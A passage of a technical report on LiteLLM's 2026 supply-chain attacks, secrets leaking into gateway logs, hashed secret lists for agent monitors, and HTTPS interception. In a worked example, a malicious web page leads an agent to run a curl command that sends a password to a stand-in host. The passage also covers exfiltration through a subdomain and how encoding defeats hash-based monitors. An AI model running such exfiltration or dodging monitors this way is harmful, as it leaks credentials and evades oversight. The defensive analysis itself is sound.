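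According to Help Net Security, the malware searched more widely for secrets than in March. It again ran whenever Python started, even if no program used LiteLLM. It looked for cloud credentials, login keys, saved browser passwords and cookies, and the files that coding agents such as Codex and Claude use to log in. A second component regularly checked a file on GitHub for the address of more code to run. The file was empty when researchers checked it on 21 October, but the attacker could have filled it later.

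The malware also tried to read the provider keys and model settings in the proxy's database, which was the only part of the attack specific to a gateway. The attempt shows that the attacker knew what a proxy stores, but the researchers who analysed the code caution that it does not prove the theft succeeded at any particular company.

The use of ordinary machine credentials is better documented. About four and a half hours after the data left the victims' systems, Wiz saw the attacker testing stolen AWS credentials for access to AI models on Amazon's Bedrock service. Criminals use such access to run models at the victim's expense, a practice called LLMjacking. The credentials came from automated build machines and Kubernetes clusters. In a few cases the attacker then listed the victim's user accounts and access keys.

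### What LiteLLM changed after October

LiteLLM began revoking every token connected with its internal systems and suppliers, whether or not it had evidence of theft. On 23 October it replaced the key that signs its Docker images. In November it moved to keyless signing, in which the build process gets a short-lived certificate for each release, so there is no permanent key to steal. Keyless signing alone would probably not have stopped the October attack, because the attacker ran the real build process and could have obtained a valid certificate.

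According to its list of posts, LiteLLM (2026) also started a trial of long-term support versions on 2 November. On 23 November it reported that the security firm Trail of Bits had reviewed the software and that fixes were still to come.

The most debatable change is a private registry, which opened on 12 November. LiteLLM will give fixes for the most severe flaws to organisations that use the registry first, and publish them for everyone else later. The company argues that attackers with AI agents can use a public fix to work out how to exploit the flaw before most users have upgraded. The first attacks came 36 hours after the April advisory, which supports this concern. But users of the public version will remain vulnerable for longer without knowing it, and will be easy targets if an attacker obtains the private fix.

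These measures make another poisoned release less likely. They do not reduce the number of keys that a running proxy stores.

### Theft from the machine and theft from the gateway

Much of the damage in 2026 could have happened through any popular package. On 27 March, three days after the first attack on LiteLLM, attackers published poisoned versions of telnyx, a communications company's Python package. Although telnyx is not an AI gateway, these versions also carried malware that stole credentials from machines where they were installed. They stayed available for 3 hours and 42 minutes.

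Many of the people at risk from the malicious LiteLLM versions in March were not running a gateway. They might never have heard of LiteLLM, because they had installed another package that depends on it. FutureSearch found 2,337 such packages on PyPI, and 88% of them would have allowed the malicious versions to be installed.

LiteLLM may still have been a more attractive target because it needs keys to work, even if the malware then just searches the whole machine. In ITPro's *LiteLLM PyPI compromise*, Kiran Raj of the security company Endor Labs observes that TeamPCP chose tools that run where valuable credentials are likely to be. Two of the other targets were security scanners.

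The three flaws in the table, by contrast, have no equivalent in an ordinary library. They could let a single stranger or user get the keys of everyone behind the gateway. The October malware also tried to get everyone's keys, by searching the proxy database. But a company could have lost its provider keys through the three flaws even if every release had been free of malware.

The precautions against the two kinds of theft can conflict. PyPI recommends lock files, which fix the exact version and hash of every package, and a waiting period, such as three days, before installing anything new. Either would have kept out all three malicious versions of LiteLLM, since PyPI blocked each of them within three hours. But a waiting period can delay a security fix, and attackers started exploiting the SQL injection within a day and a half. PyPI therefore advises combining the waiting period with a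 tool that checks for known vulnerabilities and installs fixes for them at once.

In March, LiteLLM told users to stay on a version known to be safe, such as 1.82.6, until it had verified a newer one. Version 1.82.6 contained no malware, but it did contain the SQL injection vulnerability. A company that followed the advice and then forgot to upgrade would have avoided the malicious releases, but from late April it would have been exposed to anyone who had read the advisory.

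## Secrets in LiteLLM's logs, and how to log less

Even without an attack, a LiteLLM proxy can expose keys by writing them into its records. It keeps spend logs, which show administrators who used which model and what it cost. A company can also have the proxy send traces, or step-by-step records of how it handled each request, to a separate telemetry system where engineers look for faults. In March 2026, LiteLLM reported a bug that could put credentials into both the spend logs and the traces.

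### How a safety check put keys in the logs

The bug involved guardrails, which are checks that the proxy runs on requests or replies, for instance to block personal data. Companies can write their own. LiteLLM's incident report of 18 March explains what went wrong:

1. A request arrives with headers, lines of technical information that come before the content. The Authorization header carries the key that identifies the sender. LiteLLM keeps the headers in its internal data during the call and is not supposed to log them.
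2. The company's guardrail checks the request. It only needs to return a short result, but a custom guardrail could return all the request data, including the headers.
3. LiteLLM prepares this result for logging without removing the internal data, so the key stays in it as plain text.
4. The result goes into the spend logs, the traces and any other logging service that receives the same data.

Secrets could leak only if a custom guardrail returned the full request data or something else containing the secret headers, LiteLLM logged that result in the standard way, and somebody had access to the logs or traces. A company whose guardrails returned only a verdict was therefore safe from this leak.

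Administrators with access to the spend logs and anyone with access to the telemetry system could see the keys. The bug did not let outsiders bypass the login or directly reach another customer's data.

The exposed header would normally hold a developer's virtual key, because the proxy adds the provider key later. Someone who found a virtual key in a trace could run models at the company's expense. If an administrator had tested a model with the master key, an engineer reading the traces could have taken control of the proxy.

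LiteLLM fixed the bug in version 1.82.3. Upgrading does not remove credentials from old logs, so LiteLLM also told affected users to check whether they had kept logs from when the bug was present and to replace any credentials those logs might contain. LiteLLM lists the duration of the problem as "unknown", which makes it hard to decide how far back to look.

LiteLLM's logging had exposed keys before. Aikido (2024), a security company, reported that spend logs in all versions up to 1.40.5 included the raw request, possibly with its authorization header. GitLab's *CVE-2024-9606* (2025) describes masking code that hid only the first five characters of an API key. Many keys start with "sk-", so an attacker would have to guess only two characters of those keys. If each is a letter or digit, there are 3,844 combinations.

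Other companies' logging tools can also record secrets. Braintrust, which makes software for recording model calls, found that versions 0.2.0 to 0.27 of its Python package could record provider keys, AWS keys and Azure tokens when a program passed them directly to LiteLLM.

### Tokens in agents' replies

Secrets can also appear in the conversation itself, so removing the headers does not remove them all. In October, Help Net Security reported that, according to LiteLLM, Claude Code sometimes includes a user's GitHub token in a response body, the part of a message that holds the reply. GitHub's command-line program uses this token to act for the user. If the proxy logs response bodies, it may store the token.

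LiteLLM made this observation while investigating the October attack, when it still believed the attacker had taken tokens from its logs. The Vanguard USA's *How one unrevoked key let attackers poison LiteLLM* (2026) reports that LiteLLM's final analysis traced the tokens to the agent platform and the build system instead.

The October attack is therefore not good evidence that anyone has stolen a token from LiteLLM's logs. The observation about Claude Code may still be correct, because it concerns how the agent behaves rather than how the attacker got in.

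Masking a conversation is harder than masking a header because the same information can appear in several places. In a tutorial, WiLine set the proxy to mask names and email addresses in the logs but send the real text to the model. The stored question contained placeholders, but the stored answer included the customer's name, Maria Alvarez, because the model had repeated it. Any customer support assistant will regularly repeat names like this. The proxy's spend log stored the request in another form, so a company would have to check the masking there too.

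Another option is to remove secrets before a request reaches the model. LiteLLM's documentation describes a guardrail called "hide-secrets", which searches requests using an open-source library with separate detectors for different types of key. This should keep detected secrets from the provider as well as the log. However, LiteLLM lets companies choose which detectors to run on each request, in case developers complain that detection makes replies worse. Ordinary passwords are also harder to recognise than keys with a standard format.

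### A full record and a minimal one

A monitor can avoid most of these problems by leaving the conversation out of its log. Suppose a monitor checks outgoing traffic against a list of the company's secrets. A malicious web page tricks an agent called build-7 into sending the database password to an outside website, and the monitor blocks the tool call. Here are two ways to record this:

| Field | Full record | Minimal record |
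|---|---|---|
| Time | 3 November, 14:02:11 UTC | 3 November, 14:02:11 UTC |
| Agent | build-7 | build-7 |
| Authorization header | The agent's complete gateway key | Not kept |
| Conversation | Everything so far, including a configuration file with the password Tiger-winter-58 | Not kept |
| Tool call | A shell command that sends Tiger-winter-58 to the website | Not kept |
| Destination | notes.example/new?project=payroll | notes.example |
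| Rule | Known secret leaving the company | Known secret leaving the company |
| Verdict | Blocked | Blocked |
| Matched value | Tiger-winter-58 | 7c1e09b4… (a keyed hash) |

The monitor stopped the password from reaching the website but exposed it in the log. The full record contains the password three times and the gateway key once, and anyone who can read the log can use both.

The security team can still see from the minimal record which agent tried to send a known secret, when, and where. To identify the secret, the team can compute the keyed hash of each secret on its list and look for a match. If the same hash appears the next day under another agent's name, both agents tried to send the same secret. The hash key has to stay out of the logging system.

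Even the destination can contain a secret. Web addresses often include data after the site's name, so the minimal record leaves that part out. An attacker can also put stolen data at the start of the name, for instance by making the agent contact tiger-winter-58.attacker.example. Logging only attacker.example, the part the attacker had to register, is safer.

### Fields to keep or fields to remove

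A logger can produce a short record by removing the fields that someone has marked as dangerous, or by copying only approved fields into an empty record.

When a logger works by removing secrets, anything the programmers forgot to remove goes into the log. LiteLLM's programmers knew that headers were secret, but the headers came back inside a guardrail's result, where the code did not remove them. A logger that records only approved fields leaves out anything unexpected. This follows Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults, and it is the better choice for a monitor that handles other people's passwords.

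But a list of approved fields wouldn't necessarily have prevented the March leak. LiteLLM intended to log guardrail results, so the result would probably have been an approved field, and the key inside it would still have been logged. The logger also has to restrict what each field may contain. In the example above, the verdict could be limited to "allowed", "changed" or "blocked", and the rule to a name from the monitor's list. If a guardrail then returned an entire request, it would cause an error instead of a leak.

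Approved lists take work to maintain, because useful information from a new feature doesn't appear in the log until someone adds a field for it. Removing existing fields can also break reports that people have built on them. For example, according to its release notes, LiteLLM v1.101.0rc1 no longer sends certain records about guardrails and tool calls, so users must change any saved views that depend on them.

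### How a masking step contributed to an outage

Masking keeps a field but hides the sensitive part of its value. It can hide too little, as in the five-character bug. In September 2026, masking also used up the memory of an enterprise customer's proxies.

When a call to a provider fails, the LiteLLM proxy may try again, and it keeps a note, called a breadcrumb, of each failed attempt. On 24 August, a programmer changed one line so that each breadcrumb went through an existing function that copies data and masks the credentials in it. Each breadcrumb contained a link to the list of earlier breadcrumbs. The link took up almost no memory, but the masking function followed it and copied the whole list into the new breadcrumb, which the proxy then added to the same list.

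LiteLLM says the list roughly doubled in size with each retry. In a simple version of the problem, each failure adds a new note and a copy of all the old ones, so a list of *n* notes grows to 2*n* + 1. A list that starts empty holds 1 note after the first failure, 3 after the second, 7 after the third, and more than a million after the 20th.

The outage also required two other failures at the same time. The customer's provider kept failing, so the proxy kept retrying. The proxy could not reach Redis, a database it uses for short-term data. This triggered an error handler that wrote the growing list into the log every time a request finished.

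Between 7 and 9 September, the customer's servers ran out of memory in two waves and shut down proxy processes dozens of times. One process had reached 61 gigabytes. The customer saw thousands of server errors, and clients ended tens of thousands of other requests before getting a reply.

LiteLLM had merged a fix for a later version on 3 September, but two days later it declared version 1.100.0 stable without it. Version 1.100.1 fixed the problem for this customer. According to its release notes, breadcrumbs no longer retain earlier requests. This leaves the proxy with less data to mask.

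One outage in unusual conditions is a weak argument against masking credentials, and logging them unmasked would be worse. But a masking function has to search whatever data it receives, however large or oddly structured, while copying six short fields takes about the same amount of work every time.

### How long to keep records, and who can read them

Some companies will still want full records, for example to find out why an agent keeps making the same mistake. They can limit the damage from a theft by deleting them early. If traffic is steady, a thief who steals a 30-day log gets only about 8% as many records as one who steals a year-long log.

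The number of usable passwords falls by less than this, because agents use the same ones repeatedly. A database password that agents send every day will be in last week's log as well as last year's. Early deletion helps more with customer records and confidential documents, which may pass through only once. For long-lived passwords, regular replacement works better. Data will also survive in backups and in the telemetry system's copies unless the time limit applies to them too.

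But investigators may need old records. In the October attack, the break-in came 11 days before the malicious release, so a seven-day limit would have deleted the record of the break-in before anyone noticed the attack. To find out whether anyone else had used the master key since it leaked in May, LiteLLM would have needed almost five months of access records.

Such access records need only the time, the caller's address and an identifier for the key, so a company can keep them much longer than conversations. It might reasonably keep them for a year and conversations for a week or two, though the right periods depend on how quickly the company usually discovers a break-in.

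Controlling access to timings and conversations separately also reduces the damage. An engineer looking for slow requests needs to know how long each step took, but doesn't need to read the prompts. The proxy can send timings to the general telemetry system and conversations to a store that only a few people can open. After the March bug, LiteLLM recommended restricting both the spend logs and the telemetry system to people who need access.

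The keys to a telemetry system need as much protection as the data inside it. OSV's *CVE-2025-0330* (2025) describes a flaw in LiteLLM version 1.52.1 that leaked API keys for Langfuse, a service for storing traces, when the proxy failed to read a team's settings. These keys could give full access to the Langfuse project that stored all requests. A proxy only needs to add traces, so a write-only key would have been enough, and far less useful to a thief.

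### What investigators lose

The minimal record of build-7's tool call does not show why the agent tried to send the password. The full conversation would have included the malicious web page whose instructions the agent followed. Without that conversation, the security team may never find the page, and other agents may follow the same instructions.

A minimal log also makes it harder to recover from a dishonest gateway. Liu and colleagues tested a customer-side log that keeps requests and responses, so a customer can work out which credentials passed through a bad router. If the log held only minimal records of blocked calls, the customer would have to replace every credential that its agents might have sent. Recording a keyed hash whenever a known secret passes through, even in permitted traffic, would reduce the number of credentials to replace. But it would miss any secret not already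 known.

One compromise is to keep full records only for blocked calls and encrypt them with a public key. The security team keeps the private key, which is needed to decrypt them, away from the gateway. Someone who steals the log then cannot read those records, and an attacker who takes over the gateway can read new traffic but not the old records. But an attack that the monitor fails to block leaves only a minimal record.

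Even a full log is no use to investigators once an attacker deletes it. Help Net Security reports that in October the attacker used one engineer's account to delete records of the build process, which left LiteLLM's investigators with less evidence. A company can guard against this by keeping a copy of its log, or a hash of it, somewhere the attacker cannot reach. Minimal records are safer to copy because the copy does not become another store of passwords.

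## Storing hashes instead of secrets

The monitor that blocked build-7's tool call compared outgoing traffic with a list of the company's secrets. If the list held hashes instead of the secrets, a thief who copied it would still have to guess the secrets. How much this helps depends on how easy the secrets are to guess and where the company keeps the key used to compute the hashes.

### How Microsoft Purview recognises customer records

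Companies already use hashed lists to stop employees from sending customer records to outsiders. Microsoft Purview, a set of tools for controlling sensitive data, often looks for patterns, such as nine digits arranged like a US Social Security number. But a pattern also matches numbers that don't belong to any of the company's customers. Microsoft's *Learn about exact data match based sensitive information types* describes a stricter method that looks for values from the company's own table. The table can have up to 100 million rows, and the company can refresh it daily.

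For a hospital with a table of patients, the method works like this:

1. An administrator runs Microsoft's upload tool on the table. The tool adds a salt, an extra value that it mixes into the data before hashing, and sends only the hashed values to Microsoft.
2. When Purview scans an email or document, it first looks for text that fits the pattern of a Social Security number.
3. It hashes each number it finds and checks whether the hash is in the table.
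4. If so, it looks nearby for the patient's name or date of birth. The more of these it finds, the more confident it is of the match.

Names and addresses often have no pattern, so Purview can also hash runs of words near the number and compare the hashes with the table. Administrators can set it to ignore capitalization and separators, so that 987-65-4320 matches 987654320. Netskope, which sells a similar product, lets customers treat a column as either text or numbers.

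Microsoft's *Hash and upload the sensitive information source table* recommends using two computers. One hashes the table of sensitive information in a secure environment. The other connects to Microsoft's service and receives only the hashes and the salt. This keeps the readable table off any computer that an attacker might reach through the internet. A company could do the same for an agent monitor by hashing its passwords elsewhere and giving the monitor only the result.

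Microsoft overstates the protection for Social Security numbers when it says that the method avoids sharing the sensitive data with anyone, including Microsoft. Purview has to hash the contents of new emails the same way as the table, so it needs the salt too. Anyone with both the salt and the table can hash every possible nine-digit number and see which ones match.

### How Have I Been Pwned checks a password

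Have I Been Pwned is a service that tells people whether a password has appeared in a data breach. Here the list of breached passwords is public, and the user wants to hide their password from whoever runs the service.

Have I Been Pwned's *API Documentation* explains the procedure. The user's computer hashes the password with SHA-1, an old hash function that produces 40 characters, each a digit or a letter from A to F. It sends only the first five characters to the service. The service returns the remaining 35 characters of every leaked password's hash that starts with those five, usually about 800 hashes, and the user's computer checks for its own among them. According to Cloudflare's *Validating Leaked Passwords with k-Anonymity*, this design is meant to let people check a password without disclosing its complete hash.

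Troy Hunt, who runs the service, gives the example of the password P@ssw0rd in *Understanding Have I Been Pwned's Use of SHA-1 and k-Anonymity*. Its hash starts with 21BD1. The service returned 788 hash endings for this prefix, including the one for P@ssw0rd, which was listed as having appeared 83,129 times. There are 1,048,576 possible five-character prefixes. Hunt chose five characters because four would make each reply 16 times longer, while six would make it 16 times shorter but hide the password among fewer others.

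For email addresses, the service uses a six-character prefix. An observer who suspects one of 1,000 customers can hash all 1,000 addresses, and usually only one will have the right prefix. Hunt argues that the prefix reveals nothing useful about the address, but this is true only for an observer who has no idea whose address it might be. The password prefix can also reveal a lot. P@ssw0rd would be a good guess for someone who saw 21BD1, since the four other passwords in Hunt's extract had each appeared no more than three times.

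An agent monitor could use the same procedure to avoid storing a list, by sending hash prefixes to a central service and comparing the replies with the agent's message. But it would have to ask about every part of the message that might be a password, and these parts overlap. Have I Been Pwned warns websites not to check a password after each keystroke, because someone who can see the requests arriving at Cloudflare, the company that handles its traffic, might work out the password from the series of prefixes.

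Overlapping parts of a message have the same weakness. An observer who knows one part can work out the next by finding a single new character. That character has perhaps 100 possible values, and the hash prefix almost always shows which is right. Cloudflare's *Pwned Passwords Padding (ft. Lava Lamps and Workers)* describes a way to hide the size of each reply, but hiding the size does not help against someone who can read the prefixes. It is therefore safer for the monitor to keep its own table of hashes, as Purview does.

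### Searching an agent's message for hashed secrets

A password can appear anywhere in a command or web address, often with no pattern that sets it apart from the surrounding text. The monitor therefore has to check every position. The company prepares the list on a separate computer:

1. It normalises each secret, which means putting it into a standard form, for instance by removing punctuation and capital letters.
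2. It computes a keyed hash of the result.
3. It gives the monitor the hash, the length of the normalised secret, and a label that tells the security team which secret this is.

The monitor then checks each outgoing message:

1. It normalises the message in the same way.
2. For every length on the list, it takes each stretch of text of that length, called a window.
3. It computes the keyed hash of each window and looks it up in the table.
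4. If the hash is there, it blocks the message or alerts someone.

Suppose build-7 tries to run the command "curl notes.example/new?t=Tiger-winter-58". Normalising turns this into "curlnotesexamplenewttigerwinter58", which has 33 characters. The normalised password has 13, so there are 21 windows of that length. The hashes of the first two windows, "curlnotesexam" and "urlnotesexamp", are not in the table, but the hash of the 21st, "tigerwinter58", is.

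Normalising lets the monitor catch "TIGER_WINTER_58" as well. It also makes the thief's job slightly easier, because there are fewer versions of each password to try.

### The cost of checking every window

The work depends mainly on the length of the message and the number of different secret lengths. Another secret of a length already in the table adds almost no work, since looking up a hash in a table of 1,000 takes about as long as in a table of ten. This helps because many API keys from the same provider have the same length.

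Checking a 10,000-character message against a list of secrets with 20 different lengths means hashing about 200,000 windows of text. If each keyed hash takes a microsecond, the check takes 0.2 seconds. Login systems deliberately use much slower hashes to hinder guessing. A password hash that takes 0.1 seconds is barely noticeable when someone logs in, but 200,000 of them would take 5.6 hours.

Agents usually resend the whole conversation with each request, so even the fast hash becomes slow if the monitor rechecks everything. If each step adds 10,000 characters, the 50th request has 500,000 characters and takes 10 seconds to check. The monitor can avoid this by storing the length and hash of the text it has already searched. If the next request starts with the same text, the monitor only needs to check the new part and a few characters before it, in case a secret crosses the boundary.

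Purview's approach of looking for a pattern first takes much less computation. If only five pieces of a message look like identity numbers, the monitor can check them with the slow hash in half a second. But it will miss Tiger-winter-58, which has no recognizable pattern. A sensible design might check identity numbers by pattern and search for other secrets with windows and a fast hash.

The monitor will also occasionally find a match that isn't real, because two different pieces of text can have the same hash. The expected number of false matches per message is:

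windows × stored hashes ÷ 2^(bits in each hash)

If a message has 200,000 windows and the shared table holds 1,000 hashes, 32-bit hashes produce about 0.05 false alarms per message, or one in roughly every 21 messages. With 64-bit hashes, the rate is about 10^-11 per message, which is low enough to ignore. A table of 1,000 64-bit hashes takes only 8 kilobytes, so there is little reason to use shorter ones.

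The company could split the table by length instead, so that the monitor compares each window only with secrets of the same length. If the 1,000 secrets were spread evenly over the 20 lengths, the false alarm rate for 32-bit hashes would fall to about one in 430 messages.

Very short hashes would prevent both a thief and the monitor from telling which of many possible secrets was the right one. With 20 bits, the length of Have I Been Pwned's prefix, about 950 different nine-digit numbers would share each hash, and a single message would produce about 190 false matches.

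### How quickly a thief can guess the secrets

The times below assume that a thief has copied the table and can test guesses, either because the hashes have no key or because the thief has the key too. For a fast hash, they assume 10 billion guesses a second. For a slow hash that takes 0.1 seconds, they assume 10,000 guesses a second on 1,000 rented processors.

| Secret | Possible values | Time to try all, fast hash | Time to try all, slow hash |
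|---|---|---|---|
| Nine-digit number | 10^9 | 0.1 seconds | 28 hours |
| Two common words and two digits | 10^10 | 1 second | 12 days |
| Eight random keyboard characters | 6 × 10^15 | 7 days | 19,000 years |
| Random 128-bit key | 3.4 × 10^38 | 10^21 years | 10^27 years |

The second row describes passwords like Tiger-winter-58 and assumes that both words come from a list of 10,000 and that the thief knows the format. A thief who doesn't know the format would have to try several, but the formats people use are fairly predictable.

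A fast, unkeyed hash is enough to protect random API keys, but even a slow one doesn't protect identity numbers. A slow hash somewhat delays attackers trying to recover passwords, but it is practical only if the monitor has few candidates to check.

Purview probably uses a fast hash. With a slow hash that takes 0.1 seconds per value, a single processor would need about 116 days to hash 100 million values, so customers could hardly refresh the largest tables every day.

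### Why salts and keys help less than they seem to

Login systems normally give each password its own random salt, so two users with the same password have different hashes, and a thief has to repeat every guess for each user. The server stores the salt next to the hash. When someone logs in, the server looks up the salt by username and computes one hash.

If each secret had its own salt, a monitor would have to hash each window with the salt of every secret of that length, because it doesn't know which secret the window might contain. With 1,000 secrets and a 10,000-character message, this would require 10 million hashes and take 10 seconds instead of 0.2. For a Purview table with 100 million rows, checking a single number would take 100 seconds. Microsoft's upload tool avoids this by using one salt for the whole table.

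Using one salt for all customers still makes a precomputed list of hashes useless to a thief. But the thief can check each guess against the whole table, so finding 1,000 customers' nine-digit numbers takes the same 0.1 seconds as finding one. A separate salt for each customer would raise this to 100 seconds, which would do little to stop the thief.

A keyed hash is more useful only if the key is not in the same database as the hashes. Keeping the key in an environment variable on the server would protect it from a flaw that exposes only the database, such as the SQL injection in LiteLLM, but not from the malware in the March release, which collected environment variables.

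LLM Gateway's *Hash-Only API Key Storage* describes how LLM Gateway, another proxy for language models, stores only keyed hashes of the keys it issues to users. The secret used to compute the hashes is in an environment variable that has the same value on every server. A thief with a copy of the database cannot log in with the hashes, and can test guesses against them only after also reading the variable on one of the servers. Even then, random keys would be safe.

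Replacing the hash key is awkward because nobody can convert an old hash into a new one without the original secret. LLM Gateway keeps its old hash keys for a while and tries each of them when a user connects. A monitor that did this with two keys would have to hash every window twice. Alternatively, the company could rehash the whole list from the original secrets, but it would need a safe copy of them somewhere else.

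### Keeping the hash key on a separate machine

A company can put the hash key on a separate machine that only computes keyed hashes. The monitor sends a value to this key service and gets back its hash, but never receives the key. A thief who copies everything on the monitor then cannot test guesses on their own computer. An attacker who controls the running monitor can still send guesses to the service, so the service limits how many requests it answers.

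LiteLLM's login page blocks further attempts for five minutes after more than five wrong passwords for one username from the same internet address within a minute, according to LiteLLM's *Security Best Practices*. An attacker who stays just below the limit would need about 380 years to try a billion passwords. But the limit applies to each address separately, so an attacker with 1,000 addresses would need less than five months. A key service should therefore limit total requests across all addresses.

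The limit also has to be high enough for normal traffic. If the monitor checks every window, ten messages a second would require 2 million hashes a second. An attacker allowed the same rate could try every nine-digit number in about eight minutes.

If the monitor first searches each message for patterns and finds five candidates, the service needs to answer only 50 requests a second. Trying every nine-digit number would then take about 230 days, which would give the company time to notice that the monitor was sending far more requests than usual.

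A key service is therefore worth having for identity numbers and other short values with a recognisable format, but random API keys don't need it. Passwords like Tiger-winter-58 are the hardest case because they are easy to guess but have no pattern, so the monitor has to check every window of traffic. The best solution is to replace them with random passwords.

The key service also becomes another machine that receives sensitive data. The monitor could hash each value before sending it, but the service could still guess a nine-digit number from its hash. Protocols called oblivious pseudorandom functions let the service compute a keyed hash without learning the value. They take more computing time, which matters less when each message has only a few candidate values.

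### Secrets in traffic, and secrets that no longer match

The table of hashes protects the monitor's own list but not the passwords that the monitor reads in passing traffic. BlindBox, a system for searching encrypted traffic, was designed to remove this exposure.

A proxy may also keep copies of the traffic. For example, a company can set LiteLLM's proxy to cache prompts and replies to save time and money. LiteLLM says it stores them as unencrypted text. A company might hash its database password for the monitor's list and still have the password itself in the cache.

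The method also misses any altered secret. Base64, a common way of writing data as plain letters and digits, turns Tiger-winter-58 into "VGlnZXItd2ludGVyLTU4", which the monitor would not recognise. It would also miss a password written backwards or split between two messages. The monitor can decode common formats such as base64 before searching, but an attacker who has tricked an agent can tell it to use any code, such as adding an x after every letter. Hash matching will probably catch many accidental leaks and careless attacks, but few determined attacks.

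A list of readable passwords would have some of these weaknesses too, but the monitor could at least use it to look for near matches, such as a password with one wrong letter. It can't do this with a table of hashes, because changing one letter produces a completely different hash. Purview does offer partial matching for documents such as patent forms, but Microsoft recommends that the original text have at least 256 characters, which is far longer than a password.

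### Credentials that a gateway can hash, and those it cannot

A gateway also stores credentials of its own. LiteLLM hashes those that it only has to recognise and encrypts those that it has to send onward:

| Credential | What LiteLLM does with it | How LiteLLM stores it |
|---|---|---|
| Virtual key | Recognises the developer who sends it | SHA-256 hash |
| Password for the administration page | Recognises the user who logs in | Slow hash with a random salt, since version 1.83.0 |
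| Provider key | Sends it to the provider | Encrypted |

SHA-256 is a fast, unkeyed hash, which is acceptable for virtual keys because LiteLLM generates them at random. The sample key in LiteLLM's *Virtual Keys* has 22 characters after the "sk-" prefix, enough for 128 random bits, so guessing is infeasible.

LiteLLM also identifies each key by its hash in its spend logs. Since version 1.95.0, a company can have the proxy send this hash to the provider with each request. The provider can then see which requests used the same key and trace abuse to it, but cannot use the key itself. For requests made with the master key, LiteLLM sends a fixed name instead of a hash. This is sensible because an administrator chooses the master key and might choose one weak enough to be guessed and checked against its hash.

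LiteLLM encrypts the provider keys with a key that it derives from the salt key, an environment variable. The name "salt key" is misleading, because a salt can be stored next to the hashes in a database without much harm, whereas anyone who has the salt key and a copy of the database can decrypt the provider keys. If the company hasn't set a salt key, LiteLLM uses the master key instead, so anyone who learns the master key can also decrypt the provider keys in a stolen database.

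LiteLLM advises companies to keep the salt key in a dedicated secret store and not to change it after storing any credentials, because LiteLLM could no longer decrypt them. This makes it difficult to recover from a theft of the salt key. The safest response is to replace all the provider keys and encrypt the new ones with a new salt key.

Other gateways divide their credentials the same way. LLM Gateway hashes the keys it issues and encrypts provider keys. sofatutor's *Encryption at Rest* describes another proxy that hashes its users' access tokens with SHA-256 and encrypts the keys it sends to providers.

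Hashing slightly inconveniences users, who can no longer look up a lost key. LLM Gateway shows each key only once, at creation, so anyone who loses it has to get a new one. LiteLLM's *Secret Managers Overview* describes an option to store virtual keys in an external secret manager. The option is off by default, and a company that turns it on has another collection of working keys to protect.

### How LiteLLM let users log in with a stolen hash

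A hash is safe to expose only if nobody can use it in place of the original. Until version 1.83.0, LiteLLM broke this rule for passwords to its administration page. GitLab's *GHSA-69x8-hrgq-fjj8* (2026) describes three mistakes:

- LiteLLM stored passwords as SHA-256 hashes without a salt, so users with the same password had the same hash.
- Several parts of the proxy's programming interface included these hashes in their replies to any logged-in user.
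- The login page accepted the hash itself as a password.

Normally, a server hashes whatever the user types and compares the result with the stored hash. Someone who types in a stolen hash fails, because the server hashes it again and gets a different value. LiteLLM's login code also accepted the stored hash itself as a password. An ordinary user could ask for an administrator's record, copy the hash from the reply and log in with it. The attack took three requests and no guessing. GitLab gives the vulnerability a severity score of 8.1 out of 10.

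LiteLLM confirmed all three problems in April 2026 and added that it had stored some passwords as plain text. It now uses scrypt, a deliberately slow hash, with a random salt for each password, and has removed the hashes from the replies. The slow hash makes guessing harder, but it would not have stopped the attack by itself, because an attacker could have logged in with a stolen scrypt hash if the login page had still accepted it.

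Virtual key hashes need the same care, because LiteLLM writes them to its logs and may send them to providers. If any part of the proxy accepted one of these hashes in place of the key, anyone who could read the logs would have a working credential.

Better password hashing also doesn't protect administrator logins that don't use a stored password. By default, the administration page accepts a username and password from the server's environment variables, or the master key if nobody has set a password there. Anyone who has ever read those variables can keep logging in as an administrator. LiteLLM recommends giving each administrator a separate account and then turning this login off.

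## Inspecting traffic without reading it: HTTPS proxies and BlindBox

A monitor that stores only hashes still has to decrypt an agent's messages before it can search them. Many companies already decrypt their employees' web traffic to look for malware and leaks, and researchers have measured how this affects security. Cryptographers have designed monitors that check encrypted traffic without decrypting it, though only against fairly simple rules.

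### How a company proxy reads HTTPS

HTTPS is web traffic sent over TLS. A company proxy has to read connections that employees open to other websites, whereas developers connect to a gateway directly. Administrators therefore set every company computer to trust certificates signed by the proxy. When an employee visits a bank's website, the proxy creates a certificate in the bank's name, and the browser accepts it. The proxy then opens its own connection to the bank.

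The browser can now check only the proxy's certificate, so the proxy has to check the bank's. If it does this badly, neither the browser nor the employee will notice.

In *The Security Impact of HTTPS Interception* (2017), Durumeric, Ma and colleagues found a way for websites to detect such proxies. A browser gives its name and version in a header. Its first TLS message also lists the encryption methods and features it supports, and this list differs from browser to browser. A proxy usually passes on the header but uses its own TLS software, so the header and the list don't match. For example, 82% of the intercepted connections offered a TLS feature called Heartbeat, which none of the four main browsers had ever supported.

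The researchers looked for mismatches in 7.75 billion connections from 2015 and 2016:

| Connections to | Share intercepted | Of these, less secure | Of these, severely broken |
|---|---|---|---|
| Firefox update servers | 4.0% | 65.7% | 36.8% |
| Popular e-commerce sites | 6.2% | 26.5% | 17.7% |
| Websites behind Cloudflare (US only) | 10.9% | 45.3% | 16.0% |

"Severely broken" means that an attacker between the proxy and the website could intercept and read the connection, for instance because the proxy accepts invalid certificates. The table uses the paper's detailed results, which don't match the higher figures in the paper's introduction for connections that became less secure (97%, 32% and 54%).

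Interception made 4% of the intercepted e-commerce connections and 14% of the intercepted Cloudflare connections more secure, because the proxies used better encryption than the outdated browsers did.

The Cloudflare interception rate is the least certain, because bots that pretend to be browsers can be mistaken for intercepted traffic. It was 31% before the researchers filtered out likely bots and limited the sample to large US networks. The method can also undercount interception, because it misses any proxy that copies the browser's list of features.

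Much of the interception came from antivirus programs on people's own computers, but company proxies harmed security more. Some company proxies add a header that identifies them, and among e-commerce connections with such a header, 62% were less secure and 58% were severely broken. Of twelve company proxies the researchers tested with default settings, eleven weakened the connection and five introduced severe vulnerabilities. Microsoft's Threat Management Gateway did not check certificates at all.

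These products were from early 2016, and current ones may be better. But an agent monitor that decrypts traffic could have the same flaw. Someone on the network between the company and the model provider could then pose as the provider and collect keys and prompts without breaking into the monitor.

### The NSA's advice to decrypt only once

In November 2019, the US National Security Agency (NSA) published guidance on the risks of TLS inspection. In *NSA Releases Cyber Advisory* (2019), CISA, the US civilian cybersecurity agency, encouraged administrators to review it. According to the extracts in Netresec's *The NSA HSTS Security Feature Mystery*, the NSA advised companies to decrypt and inspect traffic only once within their network, not again at a second proxy.

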